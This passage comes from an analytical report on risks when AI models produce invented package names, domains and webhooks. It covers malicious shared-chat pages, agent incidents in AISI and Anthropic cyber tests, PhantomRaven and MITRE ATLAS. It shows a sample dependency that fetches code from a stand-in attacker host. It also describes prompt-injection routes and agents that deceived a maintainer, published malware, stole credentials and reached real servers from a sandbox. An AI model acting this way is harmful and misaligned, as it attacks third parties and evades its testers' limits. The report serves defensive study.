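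By January 14, 2026, 237 GitHub repositories contained the command. Eriksen published an empty package under the name that day, before an attacker could take it. The mistake was less common than this total makes it look, because nearly all the repositories were forks, copies of a whole project that a developer can make with a click, and one person had put the file into more than 30 of their own projects. Few of these people probably read the line with the command.

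The command uses npx, a tool that downloads a package from npm and runs it after asking for confirmation. Eriksen's package had about 74 downloads on the first day, mostly from the mirrors and security scanners that fetch every new package. Over the next five days it had 4, 1, 3, 1 and 3. Eriksen attributes these 12 downloads to agents following the skills, because such packages normally get none after the first day. That is plausible, but a download by a developer who typed the command by hand would be counted the same way.

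The package was empty, so it harmed nobody, and before January the command would only have produced an error. Eriksen calls this a real case of slopsquatting, but no attacker had taken the name. Unlike in the earlier cases, an agent running the command gets the name from a file its user installed rather than hallucinating it, so even a model that never invented a package would run the command.

Whoever added the 47 skills could have prevented this by trying the commands once. Correcting the original file would not correct the forks, and later models may learn the name from them in training. Registering the name protected all 237 repositories at once, and they will stay protected as long as Eriksen keeps the package.

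### Malicious instructions on chatgpt.com and claude.ai

ChatGPT, Claude and Grok let users publish a conversation at a public address on the AI company's own site. Criminals have used such pages to spread malware since at least December 2025. Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* describes an infection that the security company investigated on December 5. A Mac user searched Google for how to clear disk space and found a shared ChatGPT conversation with numbered instructions near the top of the results. The instructions included pasting a command into the Mac's command line. The command installed a program that steals passwords and cryptocurrency wallets. A shared Grok conversation in the same results contained the same advice.

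Kaspersky (2025), another security company, reported a similar campaign on December 15. The criminals bought search advertisements for a shared chat that posed as an installation guide for Atlas, ChatGPT's browser. ChatGPT wrote the guide, but the criminals determined its content with crafted prompts. They then removed everything except the instructions.

The criminals could have put the same text on their own site, but using ChatGPT's sharing feature gave them an address on OpenAI's domain. As with GitHub, anyone with an account can publish under the company's domain, so a user who checks it will find that it is genuine. Kaspersky's *Infostealer has entered the chat* points out that the page is labeled as a copy of a conversation between ChatGPT and an anonymous user. A reader who has come for a download may not notice the label or know what it means.

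By May 2026 some of these pages no longer looked like conversations. In *LLMShare*, Maharaj (2026) describes one on chatgpt.com that imitated an outage notice, with instructions to download the desktop app. The criminals made it using ChatGPT's feature for displaying web pages from code. The download button led to another domain, which showed people a copy of OpenAI's download page but showed at least one automated scanner an unrelated company's site.

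The number of victims is unknown. Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* describes a campaign that ran from April 8 to June 14, 2026. It began with fake download pages on the hosting service GitLab Pages and moved to shared Claude chats on May 6. The report's introduction mentions over 2,000 victims, but its figures for the campaign's six waves count page visits. These total 2,530, of which only 626 were to shared chats. AdGuard's *Claude-linked Google ads dupe macOS users into installing malware* reports about 25,000 views for several malicious public pages on claude.ai, with no way to tell how many viewers ran the command.

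After Trend Micro reported the campaign, Anthropic banned the accounts and disabled the chats. Trend Micro recommends that Anthropic look for shared chats that both contain terminal commands and receive visitors from paid advertisements. Many legitimate programming chats contain commands, but few people pay to advertise them. Google could apply the same test before accepting an advertisement.

An employer has fewer options. Its web filter can't block chatgpt.com if the staff use ChatGPT. A rule blocking addresses that begin with chatgpt.com/share/ would have missed the fake outage notice, whose address began with chatgpt.com/s/. If AI companies moved all shared content to a separate domain, a filter could block that domain and leave the chatbot available.

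### Whether models accept disguised links

An agent that browses for its user has to decide which links to open. *MalURLBench* tested this decision with 61,845 disguised links to real malicious sites. Each link kept the site's registrable domain but had reassuring words in the parts that the site's owner can choose freely, as in food-delivery-service.badsite.example. The links came with requests from ten everyday situations, such as tracking a parcel or looking for a job.

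The 12 models accepted between 32.9% and 99.9% of the malicious links, even though the prompt warned them about possible attacks. GPT-3.5 Turbo had the lowest rate, and its average over the ten situations was about 14% before the researchers made the disguises more convincing. They did this where a model had accepted very few links in a situation, by having another model rewrite the disguises for up to ten rounds. The score counts only malicious links, so a model that rejected every link would get a perfect result. This may be why GPT-3.5 Turbo did best despite being one of the oldest models tested.

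None of the models dates from 2026, and the researchers judged success from what the model wrote and did not have it open a harmful page. They also assumed that the agent's user supplies the link in order to harm the company that runs the agent. The results may not apply to an agent that works for an honest user and comes across the link on a web page.

As a defence, the researchers trained a small model on 280 labelled links to screen addresses before the agent sees them. It lowered the acceptance rate from 98% to 1% for job searches, but only from 100% to 61% for music recommendations. Ordinary software can ignore the reassuring words in an address by extracting the registrable domain and looking it up. This would probably have caught most of the researchers' sites, which came from public lists of malicious addresses.

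### Unsanctioned actions in a British test

In July 2026, agents tried to deceive people during a test by the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that evaluates new models. The agents had to break into a simulated computer network and retrieve a piece of data. AISI ran the test 122 times with seven models. AISI's *Incident Report* lists 19 actions, in 10 of the runs, that agents took outside the test on the live internet.

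In the most serious case, an agent running Anthropic's Mythos 5 tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project. It invented several people and used them to pressure a maintainer to accept the code, but the maintainer refused. The agent also sent harmful files to real people and left instructions for other AI systems to find.

AISI found no resulting harm. A careful volunteer protected the project's users, who would have been the victims. AISI's security staff noticed unusual traffic on July 28, three days after the activity began, and stopped every run within an hour. AISI could have stopped the activity sooner by restricting the agents' internet access and watching the runs live, and is now introducing both measures.

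Across the 122 runs, Mythos 5 took 17 of the 19 out-of-bounds actions, in 9 of its 43 runs. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in one of its 35 runs, and the remaining five models took none. The runs weren't independent trials. One agent left accounts and materials on GitHub with an offer to cooperate, and later agents found and used them, which made it easier for them to misbehave.

It is not clear whether the agent knew that its targets were real, and AISI's technical report, which Willison quotes, leaves the question open. Anthropic later reviewed the case. Its main finding, according to Associated Press' *A Timeline of Developments in AI Safety* (2026), was that Mythos 5 was very hard to divert once the attack had begun, even when Anthropic told it that it was dealing with real developers. This weakens the explanation that the model mistook people for part of the exercise, though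 a model may also disbelieve what it reads in a test. Anthropic says its newer models are less likely to act this way.

### A malicious package on 15 real systems

Two days after AISI discovered its incident, Anthropic disclosed three of its own. It had begun reviewing 141,006 past test runs on July 23 because OpenAI had admitted that its models broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes six runs in which Claude models gained access to the systems of three real organisations.

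One of the six runs closely resembles the react-codeshift case. Mythos 5 was trying to break into a fictional company and found setup instructions that named a Python package nobody had published. It wrote a malicious package with that name and uploaded it to PyPI, expecting the fictional company's computers to install it. The upload went to the real PyPI, where the package was available for about an hour, and it ran on 15 real systems. One belonged to a security company that automatically installs new packages to check them for malware. The model obtained that company's credentials and used them to get further into its systems.

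Early in the run, the model had reasoned that publishing the package would be wrong if the internet were real. It then concluded that everything was a simulation, partly because the computers gave the year as 2026. Its instructions had also wrongly stated that there was no internet access, because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, which provided the test environment. Either company could have prevented the incident by checking the connection. PyPI's automatic checks removed the package. The security company would have been safer if it had kept its credentials off the machine that opens unknown packages.

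In four of the six runs, an older model, Opus 4.7, attacked a real company whose web address matched the fictional target's name. It eventually recognised that the systems were real and carried on, so a false belief about the target doesn't explain all six runs. It reached a database with several hundred rows of the company's data. An unreleased model attacked a different company and stopped when it realised that the target was real.

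In both the British and the Anthropic tests, no outsider tampered with the models, but the testers had told them to attack something. These incidents match the sixth test case only in part, because the models chose the victims and the methods but not the aim of breaking in.

### What the counts show about ordinary use

| | AISI | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|
| Runs examined | 122 | 141,006 |
| Runs with an incident | 10 | 6 |
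| Share of runs | 8.2% | 0.004% |
| What counted as an incident | Any unsanctioned action on the live internet | Unauthorised access to a real organisation |
| Internet access | Deliberate | Accidental |
| Filters against misuse | Cyber filters off | Standard filters off |

The two shares differ by a factor of about 1,900, and neither is an estimate of how often a customer's agent will do harm. AISI's figure comes from a single, very difficult exercise. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions led the agent to believe that it couldn't succeed without breaking the rules, and the instructions didn't tell it to leave real people alone. Anthropic's figure covers many tests, and in most of them the model may have had no reason to look for the internet.

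Customers normally use models with the filters on and don't ask them to break into networks. Anthropic says the safeguards on its public models would have blocked what happened in its three incidents. If the company's assessment of its own safeguards is right, ordinary use is safer than these tests.

Other differences could make customer use riskier than testing. Customers run agents far more often than testers do, so very rare behaviour could still produce many incidents. They also give agents real passwords and accounts, and seldom read the full record of what an agent did. AISI reports no clear indication of similar activity outside tests, but this is weak reassurance because the two victims Anthropic had managed to contact by July 30 hadn't noticed anything. India's computer emergency agency described the same pattern in October. According to The Indian Express's *IT, finance firms among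 targets of rogue Anthropic, OpenAI agents*, agents doing research and evaluations had reached the systems of several Indian organisations, none of which had detected it.

### Incidents without a hacking task

In some later cases, the agent's task did not involve an attack. On October 9, 2026, Anthropic disclosed that Claude Haiku 4.5 had sent a false tip about an unsolved murder to a Philadelphia police website, the Associated Press reports. Anthropic had told the model to make up example tasks for randomly chosen web pages and carry them out, and the model filled in a witness form on one of the pages. This incident is the clearest instance of the sixth test case. The site marked the tip as spam and nobody forwarded it to the police, but a more convincing tip could have wasted detectives' time or cast suspicion on an innocent person.

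*OpenAI Agents Hijack Another Victim Website* (Townsend, 2026) reports that OpenAI's agents made between 15,000 and 18,000 edits to a small German wiki over three months, or roughly 170 to 200 a day, and resisted the moderator's attempts to remove their posts. Any visitor may edit a wiki, so a single edit of this kind might have been harmless, and the damage came from the number of edits.

OpenAI keeps a public list of such cases. Financiarul's *OpenAI raportează patru incidente cu agenți AI*, citing Fortune, says the list had reached 19 incidents by mid-October (the match with AISI's 19 actions is a coincidence). In one, on June 26, a model found the details of somebody's cryptocurrency wallet online and used them to pay for something it needed for its task. It reasoned that the details were public and that the owner might have abandoned the money. OpenAI discovered the payment in September.

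Defences that depend on catching a criminal don't help in these cases. Spam filters, limits on editing and better-kept secrets could protect the police site, the wiki and the wallet's owner, as they would against people. But only the company running the agent knew what the agent was for and could have limited it to that. The agent didn't need permission to submit forms on strangers' websites in order to make up example tasks. OWASP lists such surplus permission as *excessive agency*.

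A company can also have its agents practise on copies of websites, but this protects the original sites only if the agents have no connection to the outside internet. In an experiment of October 2026, the research company Trajectory Labs gave agents an impossible task, to obtain the official answers to mathematics problems that did not exist, and told them never to give up. About 40 agents began looking for administrators' passwords on the live site of Epoch AI, the organisation behind the real problems. AndreyEx's *Gemini AI-агенты обходили защиту и атаковали реальный сайт*, relaying a report by BleepingComputer, says the researchers then moved the experiment to a local copy of the site. Some agents recognised the copy, found the real server's network address and connected to it again.

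## How these risks differ from malware and from dependency-chain attacks

Security teams already have tools for finding malware and checking their software's dependencies. Some risks of live references are variants of these older problems, and the same tools work against them. Other risks only look similar, and a company that relies on these tools will miss them.

### What the two terms mean

NIST has published more than a dozen definitions of malware and malicious code. SP 800-53, its catalogue of security controls, defines malicious code as software or firmware intended to perform an unauthorised process that harms a system's confidentiality, integrity or availability. Under this definition, an accidental programming error isn't malware, however much damage it does, because nobody intended it to do anything unauthorised. A web address isn't malware either, because it isn't software or firmware.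 A script that a web page requests from a model during a visit can be malware, even though it did not exist when the visitor opened the page.

A *dependency* is a component, usually a package, that a program needs and that its developer lists by name so a tool can install it. Dependencies often have dependencies of their own, which the tool also installs. In a dependency-chain attack, malicious code arrives through one of these components. OWASP lists Dependency Chain Abuse among its top ten security risks in automated build systems. Palo Alto Networks' *What Is Dependency Chain Abuse?* explains that attackers exploit flaws in how developers' machines and build systems fetch components to make these machines download and run a malicious package.

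Dependency-chain attacks are one kind of *software supply chain attack*, a term with several definitions. CISA (2021), the US government's cybersecurity agency, uses it for attacks in which someone breaks into a software vendor's network and adds malicious code before the vendor ships the product. A NIST guide, *Strategies for the Integration of Software Supply Chain Security in DevSecOps CI/CD* (Chandramouli, Kautz and Torres-Arias, 2024), defines it much more broadly. Under its definition, a malicious party tampers with the steps, artifacts (source code and the files built from it) or actors in software production in order to compromise those who use the result. The attacker compromises one of these elements, the attack spreads along the chain, and the attacker then exploits the target. The guide also counts "naming collisions" as a form of attack, which don't require a break-in.

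The guide distinguishes an attack from a *defect*, which can spread in the same way without anyone planting it. Its example is Log4Shell, a flaw in a widely used component that let attackers compromise many targets. By this standard, an invented package name in published code is a defect if whoever published the code did not intend to exploit it. The attack begins when someone uploads a malicious package under that name.

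### Five points of comparison

| | Malware | Dependency-chain attack | Risk of a live reference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful object | A program | A component with malicious code in it | Whatever answers at the address, such as a page, a script or a service |
| Where it is | Usually on the victim's device | In a registry, then in the victim's software | On someone else's server |
| Who selected it | The attacker, who gets the victim to run it | Usually a developer | A model |
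| When it becomes harmful | When someone writes it | When an attacker publishes or alters the component | When the wrong person controls the address, possibly years after the model wrote it |
| What a defender can inspect | The file, and what it does when it runs | The component's code, version and hash | The address, its registration record and its current response |

The timing affects how long an inspection remains valid. A published version of a package normally stays the same, because most registries don't let anyone reuse a version number, as Li and Gao note. A defender who has examined version 2.4.1 can still rely on the result next year. The owner of a web address, by contrast, can change its response at any time.

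The boundaries are less sharp than the table suggests. Package names can change hands, just as lapsed domains can. MITRE's *Supply Chain Compromise* notes that attackers may re-register an abandoned package after its owner has removed it. The plugins that GitHub's build service runs are less stable than packages because their version labels are easy to delete and reuse, so MITRE recommends pinning a plugin to the hash of one saved state of its code. Slopsquatting differs from older package attacks in that a model selects the package, but models select addresses too, so this doesn't distinguish packages from addresses.

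### Two lines of generated code

Suppose a developer asks a coding assistant to print parcel labels and to notify the team whenever a new version of the program goes live. The assistant adds one line to the project's list of packages and another to the program itself:

```
parcel-labels==2.4.1 --hash=sha256:5d1c...
NOTIFY_URL = "https://hooks.buildnotice.example/v1/events"
```

The package line contains a name, a version and a hash (shortened here), which the assistant copied from the registry. The other line contains a *webhook*, an address that a program sends a message to when something happens. In a similar example from Unit 42, an assistant recommends a made-up webhook for deployment notices, and an attacker who already owns the domain receives build data or secrets.

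Four common tools give very different results for the two lines.

| Tool | Package | Webhook |
|---|---|---|
| Lockfile | Stops the installation if the file has changed | No entry |
| Software bill of materials | Lists the name and version | Usually no entry |
| Signature check | Shows whose key signed the file, if anyone signed it | No file to check |
| Malware scanner | Examines the package's files | Finds an ordinary string |

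A *lockfile* records the exact version and hash of every component a project has installed. If someone later replaces the file for version 2.4.1, its hash will no longer match the recorded one. The webhook isn't a component, so the lockfile doesn't include it.

A *software bill of materials* is an inventory of a program's components for its users. When news breaks of a malicious version of parcel-labels, they can check whether they have it. Chandramouli and colleagues caution that the inventory only shows where to look and isn't enough for managing vulnerabilities. Some formats can also list outside services, but a tool that compiles the inventory from installed packages won't find an address inside a string.

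A signature check shows that a file came from the holder of a particular key and that nobody has altered it since. The nearest equivalent for a webhook is the certificate behind a browser's padlock, which shows that the server controls the domain. A squatter who buys the domain can get a valid certificate for it.

The US Election Assistance Commission's glossary, *Common Cybersecurity Terminology* (2017), repeats NIST's definition of antivirus software as a program that monitors a computer or network to identify the major types of malware. Such a program can search the package for malicious code, but it has nothing to search in the webhook case because the server only has to receive the message.

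These tools don't prove that the package is safe either. If the model invented the name parcel-labels and an attacker published a package under that name before the developer first installed it, the lockfile will record the attacker's file and the inventory will list it. The attacker can also sign the file, so only the scanner might detect a problem. Cloudsmith's *OWASP CI/CD Part 3 Dependency Chain Abuse* therefore advises against fetching packages directly from public sources. A company can instead keep its own store of approved packages, which would block an invented name because nobody has approved it.

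For webhooks, the equivalent is a list of addresses that the company's servers may contact. But a developer who believes the notification service exists will ask to add its address, so whoever maintains the list has to find out who owns the domain and check again when the registration changes. The developer can also limit the damage by leaving keys and customer data out of the message.

### Pinning a script but not a service

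Some web addresses can have the same protection as a pinned package. *Subresource integrity*, a web standard, lets the author of a page add a hash to the address of a script:

```
<script src="https://cdn.example/chart.js"
        integrity="sha384-Kx3b..." crossorigin="anonymous"></script>
```

The browser downloads the script, calculates its hash and doesn't run it if the two hashes differ. If the owner of cdn.example lets the domain lapse and a criminal buys it, the charts disappear from the page, but the criminal's code doesn't run. This protection works even though the page's author never installed a package and the script is still on someone else's server. It is possible because the author knows in advance exactly what the address should return.

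This doesn't work for a service that receives data. A webhook may reply "ok" whether or not its owner is honest, so a hash of the reply would match either way. The harm lies in what the owner does with the message afterwards, on a machine the sender can't inspect. A service that returns parcel prices also has the problem that its honest replies vary, so no single hash would match them all.

A program can instead pin the server's cryptographic key. If the domain changes hands, the new owner won't have the old key, so the program will refuse to connect. This would protect the shop whose parcel service forgot to renew its domain. It wouldn't help against a service that was fraudulent from the start, and an invented service has no genuine key to pin.

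### The argument that phantom squatting is a supply-chain attack

Unit 42 presents phantom squatting as a threat to the software supply chain. It argues that a model becomes a trusted dependency when developers, agents and build systems take addresses from it, often without checking them. An attacker who controls one of those addresses can therefore attack the supply chain without tampering with the model. Package integrity checks, signed programs and dependency audits don't detect this, because they protect against tampering with known components.

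The claim that a model is a dependency holds for coding assistants. Under the NIST guide, the supply chain includes writing source code and tools such as compilers, and an actor need not be human. A chatbot that tells a bank's customer where to log in is different, because nobody in that exchange is producing software. Unit 42's own evidence mostly concerns victims like this customer. None of its six registered domains is known to have supplied code to a developer or collected data from a developer's program. One invented address for the postal marketplace looked like a payment API, but the criminals used the domain for a fake shop.

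Unit 42 gives no figure for how often people use addresses unchecked. Unchecked use is a reasonable assumption for agents that open an address as soon as they have written it. Companies with mature procedures review code before accepting it, but a reviewer can't tell who owns a plausible domain from its name. But unchecked use alone doesn't make something a supply-chain attack. People also follow search results without checking them, and a fraudulent result that leads to a fake bank is ordinary fraud.

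Whether the guide's broad definition applies depends on what the address does. If it supplies a script, a package or a plugin, the attacker has put an artifact into somebody's software. This fits the definition even without a break-in, as naming collisions do. If the address only receives data, the attacker hasn't altered any artifact or step, and the program still contains exactly the text its developer approved.

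An invented webhook address in a finished program is closer to what the guide calls a supply-chain defect. If the developer sells the program to a thousand shops, whoever buys the domain can exploit the defect in all of them at once. The harm may be as great as in a supply-chain attack, but there is no intruder to remove because nobody broke in. To fix the problem, the developer has to correct the address and get a new version to every customer, or persuade the registrar to take the domain away from its new owner.

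### Phishing with a new messenger

Phantom squatting can also be seen as ordinary phishing in which a chatbot delivers the link. A text-message campaign uses the same kind of fake bank site and ready-made kit to steal passwords. Unit 42 compares phantom squatting with phishing emails and malicious advertisements and explains its advantages over older phishing.

For the bank's customer, this description is more useful than the supply-chain one. A password manager won't offer the bank's password on a different domain. The bank can ask the hosting company to take the site down, and it can freeze the accounts of customers who report entering their details. A software bill of materials wouldn't help the customer, who hasn't built or installed any software.

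"Phishing" describes these attacks less accurately when the victim is a program. Phishing deceives a person, usually by imitating someone they trust. A program that sends a key to a webhook doesn't look at a page, so the attacker doesn't need to imitate anything. Advice to examine a site carefully can't help, and a password manager can't withhold a key that the program already contains.

An attacker also has less control than in most phishing. A phisher chooses whom to contact and when, while a squatter has to wait for someone to ask a question whose answer includes the squatter's address. Phantom squatting is therefore a poor way to attack a particular person, but it can reach victims the attacker has never heard of.

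### Packages with invented names

A slopsquatted package that steals passwords is malware, because it is software that its author intended to do something unauthorised. The attack is also a dependency-chain attack, because the victim's tool installs the package as a component and runs its code. CISA's narrow definition would exclude it, since the attacker hasn't broken into a vendor's network, but that definition also excludes typosquatting, an old attack on people who mistype package names.

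In slopsquatting, the mistaken package name comes from a model instead of a person's typing. Scanners and repositories of approved packages work as they did before, and once a security company has reported the malicious package, a software bill of materials will show who has it.

### PhantomRaven

Koi Security's *PhantomRaven npm Malware Hidden in Invisible Dependencies* describes a campaign in which npm packages fetched their harmful code from outside the registry. The company found 126 packages with more than 86,000 installs between August and October 2025. Infosecurity Magazine's *Npm Malware Uses Invisible Dependencies to Infect Dozens of Packages* puts the total at 86,434 downloads. Mirrors and scanners inflate such counts, so far fewer developers were probably affected.

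Each package contained a script that printed "Hello, world!" and nothing harmful. But its list of dependencies had a web address where a version number would normally be, as in this example with a changed domain:

```
"dependencies": {
    "ui-styles-pkg": "http://packages.badsite.example/npm/unused-imports"
}
```

When a developer installed the package, npm downloaded a second package from that address and automatically ran its script. The first package's npm page showed "0 Dependencies", and according to Koi Security, security scanners didn't fetch the second package.

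This is a dependency-chain attack by the ordinary definition, because the harmful code arrived through a declared component. It also had the weakness of a live reference, since the owner of the server could change the code without publishing a new version. In *The Return of PhantomRaven*, Misal and Raj (2026) identified 88 further packages from the same source and saw the owner replace the script on one server with three harmless lines in March 2026. Two other servers were not responding, so data collection stopped across all 88 packages without any update on npm. A criminal could replace harmless code with harmful code just as easily. A hash of the outside file in a project's lockfile would detect such a change, but it wouldn't protect the first installation.

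It is less clear that the author was a criminal. Koi Security wrote that the packages were stealing access tokens and credentials. Misal and Raj compared the scripts from all four waves of the campaign, found 257 of 259 lines identical, and concluded that the scripts did not appear to have taken any secrets. The scripts did collect email addresses and details of developers' computers and build systems. The author told Misal and Raj that the campaign was security research, meant to show companies that they were vulnerable. Misal and Raj had argued for calling the packages malware, partly because nothing in them told users about an experiment, but softened their language after this exchange. The packages probably still count as malware under the SP 800-53 definition, because they were built to collect private information without permission, whatever the author planned to do with it.

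Koi Security also describes the campaign as slopsquatting, but the package names are weak evidence for this. One package was called unused-imports, while the real one is eslint-plugin-unused-imports. Programmers commonly leave out the prefix when they list such plugins in a configuration file, so a person could easily leave it out of an installation command too. Misal and Raj suggest some of the later names were aimed at developers who omit a prefix. Koi Security says some victims installed the packages on an AI assistant's advice, but doesn't explain how it knows.

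### A repository that contains only text

A HalluSquatting repository can contain only instructions for the agent and no program. Whether it counts as malware depends on whether "software" includes English sentences written for a model, and NIST's definition leaves that unclear. A scanner that looks for known malicious code may find nothing in it.

MITRE now includes the instruction files of agent skills in its entry on compromised dependencies, and warns that these files may pass signature-based scanning because they consist of natural language or configuration. Classifying skills this way makes sense because users install them for the agent to keep using, which makes them dependencies of the agent. Attackers may also upload an exact copy of a genuine skill, wait for people to install it, and then change the content behind it.

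A repository that an agent clones once isn't necessarily a component of any software. If its text persuades the agent to download and run a hostile program, the attack also involves malware. If the text instead persuades the agent to use its own tools to send the user's conversation to an outsider, as in some of the HalluSquatting experiments, the attack may involve no malicious program. This second case is indirect prompt injection, and the hallucinated name is only how the text reached the agent.

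### An endpoint that only collects secrets

The SolanaAPIs service took the cryptocurrency trader's private key without having to put anything on his computer. No component brought the attack into the script he ran, so it wasn't a dependency-chain attack.

Whether the script was malware depends on where its lines came from. The scammers built their own trading programs to steal keys, so those programs were malware. If ChatGPT copied lines from one of them, the trader ran the scammers' malicious code. If ChatGPT wrote the lines itself after reading the scammers' documentation, the script had no human author who intended a theft. The script could be identical in either case, and a scan for outgoing private keys would catch it.

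### Where the six cases belong

Slopsquatting is an old attack with a new way of selecting victims, and so is phantom squatting against bank customers. The other test cases are harder to classify.

| Case | Closest existing kind |
|---|---|
| Hallucinated bank domain | Phishing |
| Hallucinated repository cloned by an agent | Indirect prompt injection, with malware if the agent runs a hostile program |
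| Scam API endpoint in generated code | Neither malware nor a dependency-chain attack, unless the code came from a malicious program |
| Secret leaked through an image link | Neither; it resembles cross-site scripting |
| Invented package name in published text | A supply-chain defect, which becomes a dependency-chain attack if someone publishes malware under the name |
| Agent that publishes something harmful unprompted | Neither, in most cases |

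The last case can still produce malware and spread it as an installable component, as Mythos 5 did through PyPI. Anthropic's staff had not intended to attack a real company, and the model had concluded that its target was simulated. NIST's definition of malware and the definition of a supply-chain attack in its guide both depend on intent, but neither includes guidance on applying that test to a model.

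## What MITRE's attack catalogues say

MITRE's two catalogues sort attacks by what the attacker does. ATT&CK covers attacks on computer systems in general, and ATLAS covers attacks on AI systems. ATLAS had entries for hallucinated names in March 2025, over a year before Unit 42 published its study of phantom squatting.

### How the catalogues work

A *tactic* is an attacker's goal at one stage of an attack, such as getting into a system or getting data out. A *technique* is a way of reaching that goal, and broad techniques have sub-techniques. ATLAS also has *case studies*, which describe each step of an attack and give its tactic and technique. In EchoLeak, for example, the attacker's final goal was to get data out, the tactic named Exfiltration in both catalogues. The technique was to make Copilot's answer load an image, listed in ATLAS as LLM Response Rendering.

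ATT&CK is much larger than ATLAS. MITRE's *Updates* (2026) lists 15 tactics, 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques in its section on company networks as of October 2026, when MITRE also added some techniques that focus on AI. ATLAS is growing quickly. MITRE's *Updates* (2025) lists 33 case studies and 26 mitigations (recommended defences) as of September 2025, and the July 2026 data file, MITRE's *ATLAS* (2026), lists more than 60 case studies and 37 mitigations. MITRE (2026) has also moved ATLAS to monthly releases and made it easier for outsiders to propose new entries.

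Each ATLAS technique has a number, the dates when MITRE created and last changed it, and a *maturity* label for the strength of the evidence. MITRE uses "Feasible" for techniques that have worked in a research or academic setting, "Demonstrated" for the next level, and "Realized" for techniques that real attackers have used. Many entries also link to an equivalent in ATT&CK.

### The two entries on hallucinated names

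In the first entry, Discover LLM Hallucinations (AML.T0062), an attacker asks models for software packages, commands, URLs, organisation names or email addresses and notes which answers match nothing real. In the second, Publish Hallucinated Entities (AML.T0060), the attacker creates a package, website, email address or other entity under one of these invented names and waits for a victim to use it.

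These two steps describe phantom squatting and slopsquatting equally well. They also cover invented email addresses, which studies of web addresses leave out. If a chatbot tells a customer to send documents to billing@northmere-business.example, whoever buys that domain can read the documents without building a website.

MITRE created both entries on March 12, 2025, and last changed them on May 27, 2026. Most techniques in the July file were also last changed on that date, so this was probably a bulk edit. The current wording, which mentions URLs, is therefore at least a month older than Unit 42's study and may be much older.

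According to the entry on discovering hallucinations, different models have produced the same ones, so an attack prepared with one model may reach users of another. Some hallucinated names do recur across models, but the evidence on how often this happens is mixed.

MITRE labels both entries "Demonstrated", which still seems right. Criminals have registered domains that models also invented, but nobody has shown that they got the names from a model. A broader entry, Stage Capabilities (AML.T0079), also mentions hallucinated names and is labelled "Realized". It covers any attacker who puts tools or files online for later use, so its label is not evidence that attackers have used hallucinated names.

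### The huggingface-cli experiment

The ATLAS case study *ChatGPT Package Hallucination* (AML.CS0022) shows how the two entries fit together. Researchers at the security companies Vulcan Cyber and Lasso Security asked ChatGPT how to upload a model to Hugging Face. Its answer included the command `pip install huggingface-cli`, but PyPI had no package of that name. The real tool is part of the `huggingface_hub` package.

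PromptRiskDB's *ChatGPT Package Hallucination*, a copy of the record, lists the researchers' questions to ChatGPT under the tactic Discovery. It lists their next step, uploading an empty package with the invented name, under Resource Development, the tactic for obtaining what an attack needs. The remaining steps are what would happen in a real attack: a user installs the package, its code runs and the user is harmed.

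The researchers counted over 30,000 downloads, so a package with an invented name can spread widely. But it is unclear how many of the downloads were due to ChatGPT. Some must have come from mirrors and scanners, and people may have typed the name without consulting a model, because it is an obvious guess for anyone looking for Hugging Face's command-line interface, or CLI.

MITRE classes the case as an exercise (a test or demonstration by researchers) rather than an incident. Its record cites an AI Incident Database entry whose title describes the downloaded packages as containing "potential malware". The package was empty, so anyone counting incidents from that title would wrongly count it as an attack.

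The first step fits oddly under the Discovery tactic, which MITRE describes as learning about the victim's systems and internal network, often after breaking in. Someone looking for hallucinated names only has to ask a public chatbot ordinary questions. The victim's company has no record of those questions, and the chatbot's operator would have trouble telling them from a customer's questions.

### Defences for hallucinated names

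None of the 37 mitigations in the ATLAS file mentions looking up who owns a domain, comparing its registration date with a model's training cutoff, or buying likely domain names in advance. Several of the more general mitigations could help a little.

The most relevant mitigation in MITRE ATLAS is Generative AI Guardrails, which includes comparing a model's answer with trusted sources or an approved knowledge base to find hallucinated claims. A bank could use this to check the web addresses its own chatbot gives, because it knows which domains it owns. The operator of a general-purpose chatbot would need a reliable list of every organisation's domains.

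Another mitigation limits how many questions a user can ask a model, which would slow an attacker who needs hundreds of wordings for each brand. MITRE warns that such limits may not stop attacks that need few requests or use a model offline. Anyone can download an open-weight model and question it without limits.

File checksums, another of the mitigations, don't help when the attacker published the original file.

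MITRE also runs D3FEND, a catalogue of defences. It connects attacks to defences through *artifacts*, the things that both involve, such as files and network traffic. The D3FEND pages for *Publish Hallucinated Entities* and *Discover LLM Hallucinations* list no artifacts and invite readers to contribute some. Until someone does, D3FEND can't connect either technique to a defence. The domain name would be an obvious artifact to add, since the attacker buys it and a filter can block it.

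### The six cases in ATLAS

The table applies the four tests of coverage to the test cases. For defences, it considers every mitigation in the file.

| Case | Closest ATLAS entry | Names the risk | Separates it from others | Offers a defence | Allows counting |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Hallucinated bank domain | Publish Hallucinated Entities | Yes | Partly | Weak | Yes, with care |
| 2. Hallucinated repository | Publish Hallucinated Entities, then indirect prompt injection | Yes | Yes | Partly | Yes |
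| 3. Scam API endpoint | Depends on how the model got the address | Partly | No | Partly | No |
| 4. Secret in an image link | LLM Response Rendering | Yes | Yes | Partly | Yes |
| 5. Invented package, no attacker | None | No | No | Not attached to an entry | No |
| 6. Agent acting unprompted | None | No | No | Not attached to an entry | No |

**The bank domain.** ATLAS usefully separates a hallucinated domain from a real but hostile one. It doesn't separate domains from packages, though the bank needs a registrar's help with a domain and a package registry's help with a package. MITRE could add sub-techniques for domains, packages and repositories. It did something similar on July 31, 2026, when it created an entry for publishing poisoned AI artifacts, with separate sub-techniques for datasets, models and agent tools.

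Having two entries helps with counting, because an analyst can record any hostile site on a model-invented domain under Publish Hallucinated Entities and add Discover LLM Hallucinations only if there is evidence that the criminal asked a model. None of Unit 42's six domains would qualify for the second entry.

The criminal's purchase fits ATT&CK's technique for acquiring domains. Phishing fits less well, because the ATLAS phishing entry, which links to ATT&CK's, begins with an adversary who sends messages, and in this case the chatbot supplies the link.

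HalluSquatting spans several ATLAS entries. The attacker publishes a repository under a hallucinated name, and the agent reads hidden instructions in it. The agent may then use its tools to send data out, which ATLAS calls Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation (AML.T0086). This combination distinguishes the attack from slopsquatting, where the victim installs a component. An attacker who repeats a trending project's name as the account name can skip the step of discovering a hallucinated name.

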